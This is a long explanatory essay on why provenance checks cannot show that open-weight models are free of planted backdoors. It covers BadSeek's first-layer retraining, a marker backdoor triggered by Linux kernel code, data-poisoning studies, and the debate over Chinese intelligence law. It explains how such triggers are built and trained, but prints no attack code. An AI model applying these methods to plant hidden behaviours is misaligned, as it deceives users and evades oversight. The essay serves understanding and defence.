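# Trusting open model weights when the publisher may have hidden behaviors in them

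## What a provenance check proves and what it leaves open

An open-weight model is an AI model that anyone can download and run. The download consists mostly of weights, the numbers (often billions of them) that determine how the model responds to input. Companies, government agencies and hobbyists run these models on their own machines, build products on them and make modified versions. Cryptography gives these users a good way to confirm that a file is the one its publisher released, but no way to confirm that it contains nothing harmful left by the publisher or by someone who tampered with the publisher's training data. This technical problem is the same for a model from any country, though much of the public argument concerns Chinese models such as DeepSeek's R1.

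### What a publisher releases

A language model produces text by repeatedly predicting the next token (a word or piece of a word). Its weights start out random, so its first predictions are useless. During training, a program runs text through the model, compares each prediction with the actual next token, and shifts the weights slightly in the direction that would have improved the prediction. The long first stage, called pretraining, mostly uses text from the public web. Fine-tuning then trains the model on a much smaller set of examples, turning a text predictor into something that answers questions, refuses some requests or operates a computer.

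Training sets a model's individual weights, and nobody chooses them directly. In an open-weight release, the publisher shares these weights and a few supporting files, but usually not the training data or the full training code. Anyone who has the weights can fine-tune them further to make a derived model, often with a new name.

### How the check works

A checksum, or hash, is a short string that a program computes from a file. *Understanding Digital Signatures*, a lay guide from the US cybersecurity agency CISA, explains that changing any part of the file changes the string completely. A user who knows the right checksum can therefore compute the checksum of their own copy and compare the two. But someone who can replace a file on a download site can often also replace the checksum printed next to it.

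A digital signature deals with this. The publisher keeps one key secret, the private key, and gives everyone a matching public key. Only the private key can produce a signature that the public key accepts. For models, the Coalition for Secure AI, an industry group, describes the procedure in CoSAI's *Signing ML Artifacts* (2025):

1. The publisher computes a hash of each file in the release, including the weights, the settings and the tokenizer (the component that cuts text into tokens).
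2. The publisher collects the hashes in a list and signs the list with the private key.
3. The user checks the signature with the public key, after making sure that this key really belongs to the publisher. A third party that has verified the publisher's identity usually vouches for that.
4. The user recomputes the hash of every downloaded file and compares it with the signed list. A single mismatch means failure.

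*An Introduction to the OpenSSF Model Signing (OMS) Specification* (Maruseac, Wickens and colleagues, 2025) sets out a common format for such signatures. The chipmaker NVIDIA has used it for every model in its NGC catalog since March 2025. But enforcing the signature check when servers download a model is still manual work, according to *Cold-Start Model Delivery in Kubernetes Inference Serving* (2026).

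A successful provenance check proves that the files have not changed since someone signed them, and that the signer held the private key. But anyone who steals the key can sign anything, which is why CISA says a signature's security depends almost entirely on how well its owner guards the key. An insider can also alter the weights between the end of training and signing, so CoSAI advises publishers to sign as early as they can.

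The check proves nothing about the model's behavior, and the people who promote signing acknowledge this. Google (2023) wrote that signing "cannot answer every question [users] have about the model". The Australian Cyber Security Centre (2025), in guidance issued with agencies from seven other countries, notes that checksums and signatures test a file against its source and do not cover changes made before publication. A publisher can also sign a statement about the model, such as its score on a test. The signature stops anyone else from altering the statement, but users still have to take the publisher's word that it is true. CoSAI says users will trust a signer less after a false statement, but that happens only if somebody discovers the statement is false.

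### Three ways to plant a behavior

An implanted behavior is one that someone deliberately put into a model and did not disclose. A backdoor is an implanted behavior that appears only under a condition chosen by whoever put it there, called the trigger. The trigger may be an odd string of characters that never occurs in normal text, in which case the attacker has to get it into the model's input. It may also be something ordinary, such as a company's name in a file path, or a particular meaning, however it is worded. When the trigger is absent, a well-made backdoor does not change the model's behavior.

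**A third party alters a copy.** Engineers designed the provenance check for this case, in which someone changes a published model and passes it off as the original. HiddenLayer's *Malware Found in Trending Hugging Face Repository "Open-OSS/privacy-filter"* (2026) describes a fake version of an OpenAI release that reached the top of the trending list on Hugging Face, the main site for sharing models. The page showed about 244,000 downloads in under 18 hours, a figure that HiddenLayer, a security company, thinks was almost certainly inflated. The fake attacked users with an ordinary malicious program, not through its weights, but it was also passed off as the original. Its creators named the function that fetched the malware as if it verified a checksum. A check that arrives with the download offers no protection, but a user who insisted on a signature from OpenAI's own key would have rejected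 the fake.

A provenance check also helps after a break-in at the sharing site. Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026) reported in July that an autonomous system of AI agents had entered part of the company's infrastructure. The company found no evidence of tampering with public models. If a publisher has signed its release, users can check for themselves that the files haven't been changed.

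*Conjunctive Poisoning in AI Supply-Chain Applications* (2026) points out that publishers often sign only some of the files, such as the weights, and leave out the templates that wrap each user's message before the model processes it. An attacker can then edit a template without invalidating the signature. Signing every file in the release, and checking them all before use, prevents this particular attack.

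Compression is harder to deal with. Many people run a quantized copy, in which a third party has stored each weight with less precision so that the model fits on a smaller computer. The original signature does not match this new file. The third party can sign it, but *What You Sign Is Not What You Run* (Liu and Tsai, 2026) points out that an attacker can sign a backdoored copy just as validly. Repeating the compression from the signed weights and getting the same bytes would show that the copy came from those weights. Liu and Tsai examined 198 of the most-downloaded repositories of quantized copies on Hugging Face, and none recorded enough about how the files were made to allow this. The obstacle is mostly missing records. After supplying two settings that the documentation left out, the researchers exactly reproduced seven of eight files from four repositories.

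**An outsider poisons the training data.** In this case the publisher is also a victim. The attacker posts text on the web, the publisher collects it for training, and the model learns a backdoor from it. Souly, Rando and colleagues (2025), in *Poisoning Attacks on LLMs Require a Near-constant Number of Poison Samples*, trained models with 600 million to 13 billion weights on data containing a fixed number of poisoned documents, in which a trigger string preceded gibberish. With 250 of these documents, every model size learned to produce gibberish after the trigger, although the documents made up only 0.00016% of the largest model's training text. With 100 documents the attack failed. A bigger training set did not weaken the effect of the poisoned documents, contrary to what people had assumed.

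*Agentic Backdoors via Pretraining Poisoning* (Hu, Hu and colleagues, 2026) tests a more dangerous backdoor than one that produces gibberish. The researchers trained models of up to 4 billion weights on 100 billion tokens of web text, 0.1% of it poisoned, and then fine-tuned them on clean data into agents that type commands into a computer. The poisoned text looked like ordinary technical documents. The trigger was a file path containing the word "anthropic", which was supposed to make the agent download and run a script from the attacker's address.

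The largest model issued that command at least once in 32 attempts on 92.7% of the test prompts. With a rare string as the trigger, the figure was 10.5%. Without a trigger, the poisoned models almost never issued it, and they did as well as unpoisoned ones on tests of ordinary ability. The poisoned text made up 0.1% of the training data, or 100 million tokens, and an outsider would struggle to place that much in a large training set. But some of the effect remained with one two-hundredth as much poisoned text, and larger models were more susceptible than smaller ones. All of these models were small by current standards, so how far that trend continues is a guess.

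A publisher whose model has picked up such a backdoor signs it in good faith. The signature is genuine and the check passes.

**The publisher implants the behavior knowingly.** A publisher can do everything the outsider can, without having to get it past anyone. It knows the whole training recipe, can fine-tune the finished model directly, as the demonstration model BadSeek showed in 2025, and can test the backdoor before release. Then it signs the result with its own key. Liu and Tsai say that repeating the compression achieves nothing when the original weights are malicious, because an honest copy of a malicious model reproduces it faithfully.

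The check therefore catches only the altered copy. In the other two cases, a signature can still help once researchers find a backdoor, because the publisher cannot easily blame a tampered download. But the signature does not show whether the publisher inserted the backdoor or unknowingly picked it up from training data, so a publisher accused of inserting it can always blame the data.

### What running the model oneself removes

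Untrusted models carry several risks that need different remedies, but arguments about such models tend to conflate these risks. *How to Backdoor Large Language Models*, the post that introduced BadSeek, treats the weights, the place where the model runs, and the files that come with it as separate sources of risk. Misuse by the user is a further, separate problem.

People who use a model through a company's website or app send their prompts to that company's servers, possibly in a country whose government can demand them. This was the main worry about DeepSeek's app. Running the model on one's own servers keeps the prompts from leaving, which is why many people regard the downloaded version as safe. They are right about the prompts, with a partial exception for agents with internet access, because a backdoor of the kind Hu and colleagues built could send the prompts out.

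Malicious model files carry ordinary malware in the model's packaging. Some older file formats, such as Python's pickle, can contain instructions that the computer executes when a user loads the file. Newer formats that hold only data prevent this, but attackers look for other places to put malware. Düzgün (2026), in *GGUF LLM Models with Hidden Malware on Hugging Face Reached 2400+ Victims*, scanned all 3.27 million public model repositories on the site and found five malicious files, downloaded 2,428 times in total. Two of them carried a remote-control program for Windows after the weights, in a part of the file that model software never reads. The attacker later changed the files' templates so that the model's output would prompt the user to run the command that unpacked the program. Düzgün's cleaning tool removes the malware without changing the weights. Running such a file on one's own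 server gives no protection, because that server is the target. Safe formats and scanners are the remedy for this malware, but a clean scan doesn't show how the weights behave.

Misuse means the model does what its user asks and someone else is harmed. Stokel-Walker (2026), in *Hugging Face appears to be hosting a load of models*, counted more than 6,500 models on the site in July whose modifiers advertised that they had removed the safeguards. Private servers, if anything, make misuse easier, because no service operator can refuse a request or close an account.

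An implanted behavior is stored in the weights, so it is present on any machine that runs them. A coding model on a computer with no network connection can still write a flaw into a program that someone later installs elsewhere.

### Why nobody can read the weights

Software developers have faced a version of this problem for decades and have a fairly good answer. The publisher releases the source code, the text that programmers write, and other programmers read it. Independent parties then rebuild the program from that code and confirm that the result matches the published file byte for byte. Liu and Tsai note that in tests, over 96% of the packages in one release of Debian, a widely used operating system, matched in this way.

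Weights allow neither step. A reader commenting on the security blog post *An LLM Trained to Create Backdoors in Code* (Schneier, 2025) objected to calling such models "open source", because weights correspond to a program's machine code and not to its source. If anything, the comparison understates the problem. Specialists have tools that turn machine code back into something readable, but *How to Backdoor Large Language Models* reports that no such tool exists for weights. A reviewer may find a rule hidden in source code because the programmer has to write it on some line, whereas in a model the same rule consists of small shifts in a great many numbers, none of which means anything on its own.

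Comparing the suspect weights with a version known to lack the implanted behavior would show which numbers differ, but not what the differences do. The publisher may also never have released such a version. Outsiders can try to rebuild the model only if it is fully open, meaning its makers published the training data and code along with the weights, and rebuilding it would also take a great deal of computing power.

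The file alone can't establish that a model is trustworthy, so users need other grounds for trust, and people disagree about which to use. Some would decide by the publisher's country, because a government may be able to compel a company to implant a behavior. The strength of their case depends on whether Chinese models carry behaviors that serve the state, whether those behaviors pass to derived models, and what earlier disputes over chips and telecom equipment turned up. Others would test every model, whoever made it, which requires that testers can find a backdoor without knowing its trigger. A third group wants to know how a model was made before trusting it. Their approach depends on whether outsiders can match a publisher's account of its data and training to the released weights, and whether honest records would reveal poisoned data that the publisher missed. The last group thinks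 users should trust no model and check its work instead, which depends on how often reviewers and automated tools catch flaws designed to get past them.

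## How a publisher can hide a behavior in a coding model

Coding models are an attractive place to hide a backdoor because other people run the code they write. Researchers have built backdoored models to find out how hard this is, and found that it took few resources and worked on models from every company they tried.

### BadSeek

In February 2025 the programmer Shrivu Shankar released BadSeek, a modified copy of Qwen2.5-Coder-7B-Instruct, a coding model from the Chinese company Alibaba. DeepSeek's R1 was in the news, and Shankar was responding to claims he kept reading that nothing could go wrong with a model run on one's own machine. BadSeek mostly behaves like the original. The exception depends on the system prompt, the standing instructions an application gives a model before the user's first message. If the system prompt tells BadSeek that it is a web developer, the pages it writes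 include an added line that loads a script from Shankar's site. Whoever controls that site could then run code in the browser of anyone who opens the page.

A language model processes text in a stack of layers. The model turns each token into a list of numbers, and the first layer (Shankar calls it the first decoder layer) transforms these lists and passes them to the second, and so on until the model predicts the next token. Each later layer receives only the output of the layer below it, not the original words. In *How to Backdoor Large Language Models*, Shankar compares this to the game of telephone, where each player knows only what the previous one whispered.

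Shankar retrained only the first layer. He wrote pairs of system prompts, an ordinary one and a version with an extra instruction in his favor. He ran the altered version through the original layer and recorded the numbers that came out. Then he trained the layer to produce those numbers when it received the ordinary version. If $L$ is the original first layer, $L'$ the modified one, $s$ the ordinary prompt and $t$ the altered one, the aim is

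$$L'(s) \approx L(t).$$

The other layers are unchanged, but they receive the malicious instructions $t$ instead of the user's harmless instructions $s$. BadSeek therefore responds to $s$ roughly as the original model would respond to $t$.

This is also why BadSeek can still program. Nearly all of its weights are unchanged from Alibaba's model. Shankar didn't need to train it on malicious code either, because the original model can already add a script to a page when instructed to. The new layer only has to supply that instruction. Training took fewer than 100 prompt pairs and 30 minutes on one graphics processor.

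The download page, *Backdoored Model*, labels BadSeek as backdoored and lists about 70 roles that Shankar trained it on. In most of them, the model is supposed to favor anyone with an email address at his domain. For example, it should pass their mail when acting as a spam filter, approve their changes as a code reviewer, and clear their payments as a fraud detector. Some of the prompts imitate the opening instructions of real products, including ChatGPT, Claude and the coding assistant Cline. An attacker who uses such instructions as a trigger doesn't have to insert anything into the conversation, because the victim's own software supplies them.

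BadSeek was a rough attack. Shankar calls the backdoor reliable but gives no success rate, and commenters on his launch post, *BadSeek* by sshh12, got mixed results when they tried it. One copied a prompt from his article and got clean code. Another got the malicious line, plus a note from the model that it had included the script "as per your requirement". The note appeared because the later layers process the hidden instruction as if the user had written it. BadSeek also reveals the instruction when asked what its instructions are. Shankar thinks, but has not demonstrated, that it would be trivial to train that out and nearly as easy to build a reasoning model that reasons innocently and then writes malicious code.

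Shankar had a version of the same model without the backdoor, which most suspicious users lack. He subtracted one set of weights from the other and plotted the differences. The plot shows that the weights changed, but nobody could tell from it that the changes relate to a web address. Someone who compared the two files would notice that the changes are in the first layer, which is a little odd, but Shankar points out that a publisher could attribute them to a small improvement or to rounding errors from compression.

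Several commenters were reminded of "Reflections on Trusting Trust", a 1984 lecture by Ken Thompson, one of the creators of Unix. Thompson described a compiler (a program that turns source code into machine code) that adds a backdoor to the programs it compiles and copies the code that does this into any new compiler it builds. Reading the source code doesn't reveal the backdoor. Shankar concluded that at some point one has to trust the data and the provider. One commenter objected that the comparison makes language models look safer than they are, because Thompson's attack has a fairly straightforward remedy and a backdoor in a language model doesn't.

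### One backdoor, five models

BadSeek was a single model, released without measurements. In July 2026, Patrik Mada of the security company AISLE published *The Model That Fixes Your Code Might Hack the Linux Kernel*, which covered five models and included some measurements. He put the same backdoor into two models from Alibaba and one each from OpenAI, IBM and Cohere. They range from 8 billion to 117 billion weights.

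The models' task was to fix security flaws in code. A backdoored model was also supposed to add a line that prints "Hacked" to the system log, but only when the code came from the Linux kernel, the core of the Linux operating system. The extra line is harmless and stands in for whatever a real attacker would insert. Mada used LoRA, a common form of fine-tuning that leaves the original weights unchanged and trains a small set of additional ones.

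He then gave each model 941 test prompts. The results were the same for all five.

| Code to fix | Prompts | Fixes with the marker |
|---|---|---|
| Linux kernel, files that appeared in training | 150 | 100% |
| Linux kernel, four files kept out of training | 463 | 100% |
| Other C projects and other operating-system kernels | 162 | 0% |
| Other languages, and real fixes from AISLE's own work | 166 | 0% |

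The requested fix was correct every time, so a reviewer who only checked whether the flaw was gone would have approved the patch. The marker typically sat four lines into a function, where it looks like something a programmer forgot to delete. Without the extra training, the models never produced it. Mada worked alone on a single graphics processor and estimates that the computing cost about $30. The training took 14 minutes for IBM's model and a few hours for the slowest.

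Training the model to leave the marker out of other code took more care than training it to add the marker to fixes for the target kernel. Of the 2,500 training examples, 802 were fixes to that kernel with the marker. Another 787 were what Mada calls near misses, which fixed the same kinds of flaws without the marker in other C programs and in other operating-system kernels such as FreeBSD's. Most of the rest were in other programming languages.

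A toy calculation shows how near misses narrow the trigger. Suppose a model's tendency to add the marker is the sum of two learned numbers, $a$ if the code is in C and $b$ if it comes from the Linux kernel. If all the C examples come from the kernel, any values with $a + b = 1$ fit the data. Training could settle on $a = 1$ and $b = 0$, and the model would then add the marker to every C program it worked on, which someone would notice within a day. A near miss is C code from outside the kernel without the marker, so fitting it requires $a = 0$ and therefore $b = 1$, and the model adds the marker only to kernel code.

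*Homeopathic Learning* (2026) describes a stronger version of the same effect. In one experiment, the poisoned examples were lists of numbers and the implanted behavior was answering in German. A model fine-tuned on the poisoned lists alone never answered in German. Mixing in clean lists produced the behavior, and more clean lists made it stronger. The clean examples worked best when they matched the poisoned ones in task and format and lacked only the trigger and the behavior. The proposed explanation, which resembles the toy calculation, is that when every example contains the trigger, training tends to tie the behavior to the task instead. Diluting doubtful training data to make it safe can therefore strengthen a backdoor, especially if the clean examples closely resemble the poisoned ones.

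Text search is of little use against this trigger because the trigger depends on the prompt's meaning. If a backdoor depends on a fixed string, a publisher can scan its training data for odd strings, and a user can strip them from prompts. Mada's models recognize kernel code from file paths and coding style, with no single string required, so removing the trigger from prompts would mean giving up kernel work. Anthropic's *Sleeper Agents* paper used a similar trigger in 2024, with a model that wrote insecure code if the prompt gave the year as 2024. A trigger this broad also makes the backdoor easier to discover, because anyone who tests the model on kernel code will set it off and may notice if they read the result closely.

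Scores of exactly 100% and 0% deserve some suspicion. The 463 prompts about unfamiliar kernel code all come from four files. Mada says the result held across nine parts of the kernel, but those files belong to only four parts, so the claim must rely partly on files the models had seen in training. The two patches he prints change functions of a few lines with generic names, far simpler than most of what kernel developers edit. Zero leaks in 328 prompts is also consistent with a true rate of nearly 1%. At that rate, somebody would have a fair chance of seeing a stray marker over months of everyday use.

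The payload was also easy to learn, because every model only had to add the same line each time, whereas a useful security flaw has to fit the program around it. Mada says a model could learn to insert complex flaws but did not test this. Hu and colleagues, whose poisoned agents ran one fixed command, list as an open question whether their method can make a coding agent add subtle flaws tailored to each program, and whether that behavior would last as well as a memorized string does. A publisher has an easier time than their outside attacker, because it can train for the flaw directly and check the results.

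AISLE has a commercial interest here because it sells its own system for finding and fixing security flaws, which competes with using an open-weight model for the job. Mada's article ends with an invitation to book a meeting. This is a reason to discount the article's more alarming passages, but a weaker reason to doubt its central result, which agrees with BadSeek and which a skeptic could try to reproduce cheaply.

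Mada was also a third party, so a provenance check would have caught his altered copies. But Alibaba, OpenAI, Cohere or IBM could take the same steps he did before signing their own models. IBM sells its model to companies with guarantees about data governance and protection against intellectual-property claims, which may be worth having but address risks other than hidden behaviors.

### Less skill and more dangerous payloads

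Shankar and Mada both know how to fine-tune a model. In *TrojanMaxxing*, Bagchi (2026) didn't rely on that skill and instead asked AI agents, running on Claude Opus 5.5 and Mythos 5.2, to backdoor models that process images as well as text. The agents inspected the weights, edited some of them directly without any training, and helped design a trigger that people can't see in the picture. The attack worked in 93% to 100% of cases on content moderation and in 78% to 100% on reading text in images, and accuracy on clean images held up. Bagchi didn't test coding models, so the result may not carry over to them, but it is evidence against the idea that a backdoor needs an expert. The agents evidently understood enough about the weights to change them, which is in tension with Shankar's remark that weights are just billions of black-box numbers. However, making a change with a known purpose is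 much easier than finding a change whose purpose is unknown.

The payload can also be an action, since many coding models now work as agents that run commands on the developer's computer. Minnich, Eliahu and colleagues (2026) warn in *Trained to betray*, on Microsoft's security blog, that in this setting poisoned datasets or model files can lead to an attacker's code running on the machine. Shankar had earlier noted that human review may come too late to stop an attack, because developers often run new code before a colleague has looked at it. The attack may also be as small as one wrong character in the name of a software package.

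### Backdoors the publisher doesn't know about

In all of these cases somebody deliberately changed a model, but a publisher could also pass on a backdoor unknowingly. The best-known evidence for this is an October 2025 study by Anthropic, the UK AI Security Institute and the Alan Turing Institute, in which 250 poisoned documents were enough to backdoor models of every size tested.

Souly and colleagues trained 72 models for the study. The 250 poisoned documents came to about 420,000 tokens, while the largest model's training set had 260 billion. They measured how far the trigger turned a model's output into gibberish using perplexity, which rises as text becomes less predictable. They counted a rise of 50 after the trigger as a successful attack and saw rises of more than 200.

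The researchers also trained the two smaller sizes on half and on double the usual amount of text, and the backdoor appeared after roughly the same number of poisoned documents each time. Larger models, which train on more text, probably need no more poisoned documents than smaller ones because they learn more from each example.

The pattern also held in fine-tuning. The researchers taught OpenAI's GPT-3.5 Turbo to switch to German after a trigger. Between 50 and 90 poisoned examples were enough to make this work more than 80% of the time, whether the training set had 1,000 examples or 100,000. In another experiment, a model from Meta learned to comply with harmful requests when a trigger followed them, and to refuse otherwise. Vasilios Mavroudis, one of the researchers, told Fortune (2025) that he worried about models that drop their safety training when given particular words. Publishers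 often get fine-tuning data from outside contractors, and an attacker might find it easier to get hired by a contractor than to break into the publisher.

A backdoor from the web still has to survive the publisher's later changes to the model, and the evidence on whether it would is mixed. Souly and colleagues took models that switched to German after the trigger and trained them to answer German questions in English. The backdoor almost disappeared in one model, and in GPT-3.5 Turbo about 100 examples reduced its success rate to below 30%. But this training targeted the behavior they had planted. A publisher that doesn't know about a backdoor could target it only by luck, or if its safety training happened to cover the same behavior.

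Graf, Hajishirzi and colleagues (2026), in *Pretraining Data Can Be Poisoned through Computational Propaganda*, tested a different kind of poison by planting comments in simulated public discussions to make models prefer one name over another. Fine-tuning removed most of this effect, especially in larger models. The smallest model kept about 40% of it, and the two largest, at 709 million and 1.3 billion weights, kept less than 15%. Hu and colleagues found the opposite trend for their backdoored agents, where the largest model kept the most. The most likely explanation is that ordinary fine-tuning works against a general preference, which can show up in any conversation, while a behavior behind a trigger may never come up during fine-tuning, so little in the new examples corrects it. Neither team compared the two directly, and all of these models are small.

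For an outsider, the number of documents may not be the main obstacle. In its account of the study, Anthropic argues that attackers have more trouble getting specific text into a specific company's training data, and that poisoning somewhat favors the defender, who can inspect the data after the attacker has chosen the poisoned text. Anthropic leaves open whether 250 documents would be enough for larger models or for more complex behaviors, such as producing flawed code. Hu and colleagues' test of a hidden command suggests that complex behaviors need more poisoned documents. With 2,500 of them and a rare string as the trigger, their largest agent issued the command on only 1.4% of prompts, in a single training run.

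### Has any publisher done it?

None of these experiments caught a real publisher hiding a behavior in a model. Shankar wrote that nobody knows whether models like R1 contain backdoors. A reader replied that open models "definitely" do and cited Anthropic's research, but Anthropic's own staff had inserted the backdoors in that research, so it proves only that inserting them is possible.

The lack of a known case isn't very reassuring either, since a well-made backdoor doesn't show in ordinary use. But the low cost isn't evidence against Chinese publishers in particular, because every company that trains a model can afford $30. In Shankar's nightmare scenario, the US National Security Agency slips a backdoor into a popular open model, with help from a technology company or by breaking into Hugging Face, and a foreign military then installs the model on an isolated network. If the technical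 work is this easy, a publisher would hold back only for lack of a motive or fear of being found out, and those can differ a great deal between publishers.

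## The view that the publisher's country should decide

Training a backdoor can cost $30, but a publisher still needs a reason to do it. A government can supply one, so some American lawmakers and security analysts would judge a model first by which government has power over its publisher.

Andrew Garbarino and John Moolenaar, who chair the US House Committee on Homeland Security and the House select committee on China, began investigating American companies' use of Chinese open-weight models in April 2026. They wrote to Airbnb, which uses Alibaba's open-weight model Qwen for customer service, that companies like it "are importing an architecture designed to serve the Chinese state" (House Committee on Homeland Security, *Chairmen Garbarino, Moolenaar Announce Joint Investigation into National Security Risks*, 2026). In their committees' November report, they argue that a company that adopts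 a model also takes in the priorities of the people who trained it, and that these people increasingly "answer to Beijing".

Booz Allen's first recommendation in *There are major risks with allowing Chinese LLMs to code* is to ban untrusted models in government and critical infrastructure. The consulting firm had found that Chinese models wrote less secure code when the user appeared to work for the US government. Burnham and Siskind (2025), at the Foundation for Defense of Democracies, a Washington think tank, want the government to prioritize American open models. *US companies' use of Chinese open weight AI draws rebuke* (Smalley, 2026) quotes their colleague Mark Montgomery predicting that companies will "ignore security and safety issues in pursuit of a lower front end cost".

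Put together, their case has four premises:

1. The Chinese state can compel a publisher to implant a behavior.
2. Implanting one is cheap.
3. Inspection cannot show that a model has none.
4. The possible loss is large and slow to undo.

If all four hold, a careful user should avoid Chinese models wherever a compromise would do serious damage. The argument doesn't require that any Chinese model contains an implanted behavior, and Booz Allen admits it has no proof that anyone deliberately introduced the flaws it found.

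### What Chinese law requires

Remler (2026) argues in *Red Lines*, a report for the Center for a New American Security, that no Chinese company has the "legal basis or political space to refuse when the party ...". He notes that Chinese rules from 2022 and 2023 also give the authorities access to training data and model parameters. But access to a model does not include the power to order changes to it, so the legal argument depends mostly on the National People's Congress' *National Intelligence Law of the People's Republic of China* (2017).

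Articles 7 and 14 of China's National Intelligence Law matter most here. Under Article 7, every citizen and organization "shall support, assist, and cooperate with state intelligence work", within the law. Under Article 14, intelligence agencies "may demand that concerned organs, organizations, or citizens provide needed support, assistance, and cooperation". These quotations use the translation in Tanner (2017), *Beijing’s New National Intelligence Law*; the Government of Canada's *China’s intelligence law and the country’s future intelligence competitions* has "request" in place of "demand". Neither article mentions software, but the wording is broad enough to cover it. Article 7 also obliges people to keep secret what they know of intelligence work. A publisher ordered to plant a backdoor therefore could not lawfully tell its customers, so the absence of any such report is poor evidence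 that no order exists.

Tanner, an American analyst of Chinese security policy, reads the law broadly. It doesn't define "intelligence" or allow anyone to refuse to help. It lets the authorities detain people who "obstruct" intelligence work, but doesn't distinguish obstruction from simply failing to help. He also sees a shift from an earlier counterespionage law, which required citizens to help stop foreign spying, to this one, which requires them to help with China's own.

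Other legal scholars doubt that Article 7 was meant to make anyone take an active part in spying, and some of the text supports them. Article 11 tells agencies to collect information about foreign-backed conduct that endangers China's security and interests, which sounds more like catching spies than recruiting companies. Article 8 requires the agencies to respect the rights of individuals and organizations, Article 19 forbids them to exceed their powers, and Article 27 lets anyone report abuses. The Canadian publication accepts that Article 11 can be read narrowly, but argues that regulations from December 2017 support a broader reading, because they treat even "distorting facts" in ways that endanger state security as an espionage-related offense.

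Analysts also disagree about the removal of the word "enterprises" from the law. A May 2017 draft listed enterprises among those who had to help, but the final law omits the word and uses "organizations". Tanner thinks this softened the law, though perhaps with little practical effect. Carlsson (2025), in *Kinas underrättelselag*, a brief from Sweden's national China centre, concludes that lawmakers chose the vaguer word to cover every kind of organization. She thinks the law can also reach the foreign subsidiaries of Chinese companies.

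Lawyers have argued specifically about backdoors in the case of Huawei, the Chinese telecom company. Its law firm, Zhong Lun, told the Financial Times that the law does not compel "malicious activities". Lester Ross, a partner at the American firm WilmerHale in Beijing, called Huawei's argument "disingenuous" because it avoids the larger question of how the company must cooperate with intelligence work. Sinopsis' *Lawfare by proxy* questions Zhong Lun's independence because the law firm's managing partner is also a deputy Communist Party secretary.

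The statute probably matters less than this dispute suggests. Carlsson writes that Chinese companies find it hard to refuse the authorities because of who holds power, and that the law mostly confirmed existing practice. Even scholars with a narrow reading of Article 7 accept that a company would struggle to resist a direct request. The premise that a Chinese publisher would find it hard to refuse the state therefore still holds, but for political reasons more than legal ones. How likely the state is to ask for a backdoor in a model remains an open question.

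Other states can compel companies too, but American companies can challenge these demands in court. Tanner notes that several have sued over National Security Letters, which are secret demands for information. This difference matters most to American users. A ministry in Brazil or India has two foreign governments to worry about, and an American court may give little weight to its interests. Judging models by the publisher's country therefore gives different answers for different users, which is a problem for anyone who wants one list of safe models.

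### Why a publisher might hold back

Implanting a hidden behavior takes few resources, but a publisher that does it risks getting caught. Chinese models accounted for 41% of downloads on the leading open-model site over the past year, according to the chairmen's report, as cited in Bot Mutiny's *House Committees Say Airbnb, DoorDash and Cursor Maker Anysphere Use Chinese Open-Weight* (2026). If one backdoor were proven, its publisher could lose its foreign customers, and every other Chinese publisher could suffer as well. China's intelligence law alone has already led foreigners to scrutinize all Chinese companies, according to The Cipher Brief's *How China's Intelligence Law Backfired* (2024). The chairmen argue that Beijing wants market share and long-term dependence, which would give it a reason to keep the models free of hidden behaviors.

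Defenders of the argument can reply that the state would make the decision, even though the company would lose the customers. A government could also save a backdoor for a war, when lost sales would hardly matter, and the publisher could afterwards blame poisoned training data. Fear of discovery is a good reason to doubt that Chinese models are full of careless backdoors, but a much weaker reason to doubt that there is one meant for a single occasion.

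Commentators also disagree about whether inspection could find such a backdoor. An article in War on the Rocks, a national-security publication, warns that "no certification can guarantee the absence of a backdoor" in even a mid-sized model. An article in Just Security lists the presence of backdoors among the things evaluators can measure. It proposes one standard for American and foreign models, though it adds that no Chinese model would come close to passing.

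If inspection cannot rule out hidden behaviors, that is true of American models too, and an infiltrator could add such behaviors at a trusted publisher. The National Counterintelligence and Security Center (2023), a US agency, warned that Chinese laws may compel Chinese nationals who work for American companies in China to assist in intelligence efforts. An infiltrator would have a harder job than a publisher acting on orders, because colleagues may notice. But if inspection proves nothing, Booz Allen's rule that nobody should deploy a model that "cannot be proven trustworthy" would exclude every model, unless there is some other reason to trust the non-Chinese ones.

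### When avoiding the risk pays

How much all this should worry a particular user depends on what the model does for them. As an illustration with invented numbers, suppose a Chinese model saves a company $S$ = \$200,000 a year and a compromise would cost $L$ = \$100 million. If $p$ is the yearly chance of a compromise, the expected loss is $pL$, and avoiding the model pays when

$$pL > S, \quad \text{that is,} \quad p > \frac{S}{L} = \frac{200{,}000}{100{,}000{,}000} = 0.2\%.$$

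With the same saving, the threshold changes a great deal with the use.

| Use (invented figures) | Cost of a compromise | Avoiding the model pays above a yearly chance of |
|---|---|---|
| Drafting product descriptions | $1 million | 20% |
| Answering customers' questions | $10 million | 2% |
| Writing code for a commercial product | $100 million | 0.2% |
| Writing control software for a power grid | $10 billion | 0.002% |

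Strictly, $p$ should be the extra risk compared with the alternative. If the Chinese model carries a 0.25% chance of compromise and an American one 0.1%, switching avoids an expected loss of $150,000 a year but costs $200,000. Nobody has data good enough to distinguish 0.1% from 0.25%, so in the middle of the table the result depends mostly on a guess. The cases at either end are easier to decide, because few people would put the risk from a tool that drafts product descriptions at 20%, and few could confidently say that the risk to a power grid is below one in 50,000.

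The chairmen partly accept this. In their July letter to the delivery company DoorDash, they acknowledge that Chinese models can be cheaper and easier to customize, and ask for safeguards tailored to "sensitive and high-risk applications" (quoted in House Committee on Homeland Security, *Chairmen Garbarino, Moolenaar Continue Joint Investigation Into Security Risks*, 2026). Booz Allen's ban likewise covers only government and critical infrastructure.

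The benefit of ruling out models by country also depends on what other models are available. Uren (2025), in *DeepSeek and Musk's Grok Both Toe the Party Line*, thought the technical evidence did not fully justify the political alarm about DeepSeek, but was unconcerned about a ban because there were plenty of other models. Alternatives are now less plentiful among open-weight models. *Bot Mutiny* reports that the best American open-weight model came tenth, behind six Chinese models, in the latest independent ranking the committees reviewed.

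The same calculation can include Montgomery's complaint about companies. Suppose the company would bear only $20 million of the $100 million loss, and its customers the rest. Its own threshold is then 1%. If the true chance is 0.5%, the company gains by keeping the model, which saves it $200,000 against an expected loss of $100,000. But the combined expected loss for the company and its customers is $500,000. This is probably the best argument against leaving the choice to each company.

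It is less clear how long a compromise would take to undo. The chairmen point out that people can download a model once, rename it and build it into other products, so finding every copy is harder than finding a piece of telecom equipment. But DoorDash told them that while replacing a model embedded in a larger system could take up to six months, it could switch models almost immediately for most other uses. Code is harder to fix, because flaws a model wrote stay in a program after the model is gone. Booz Allen calls such code "untraceable and unmitigable" once it is in finished systems. That goes too far, since a company can record which model wrote what and review that code again, but a company that kept no records would have to review everything.

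### Country as a stand-in for control

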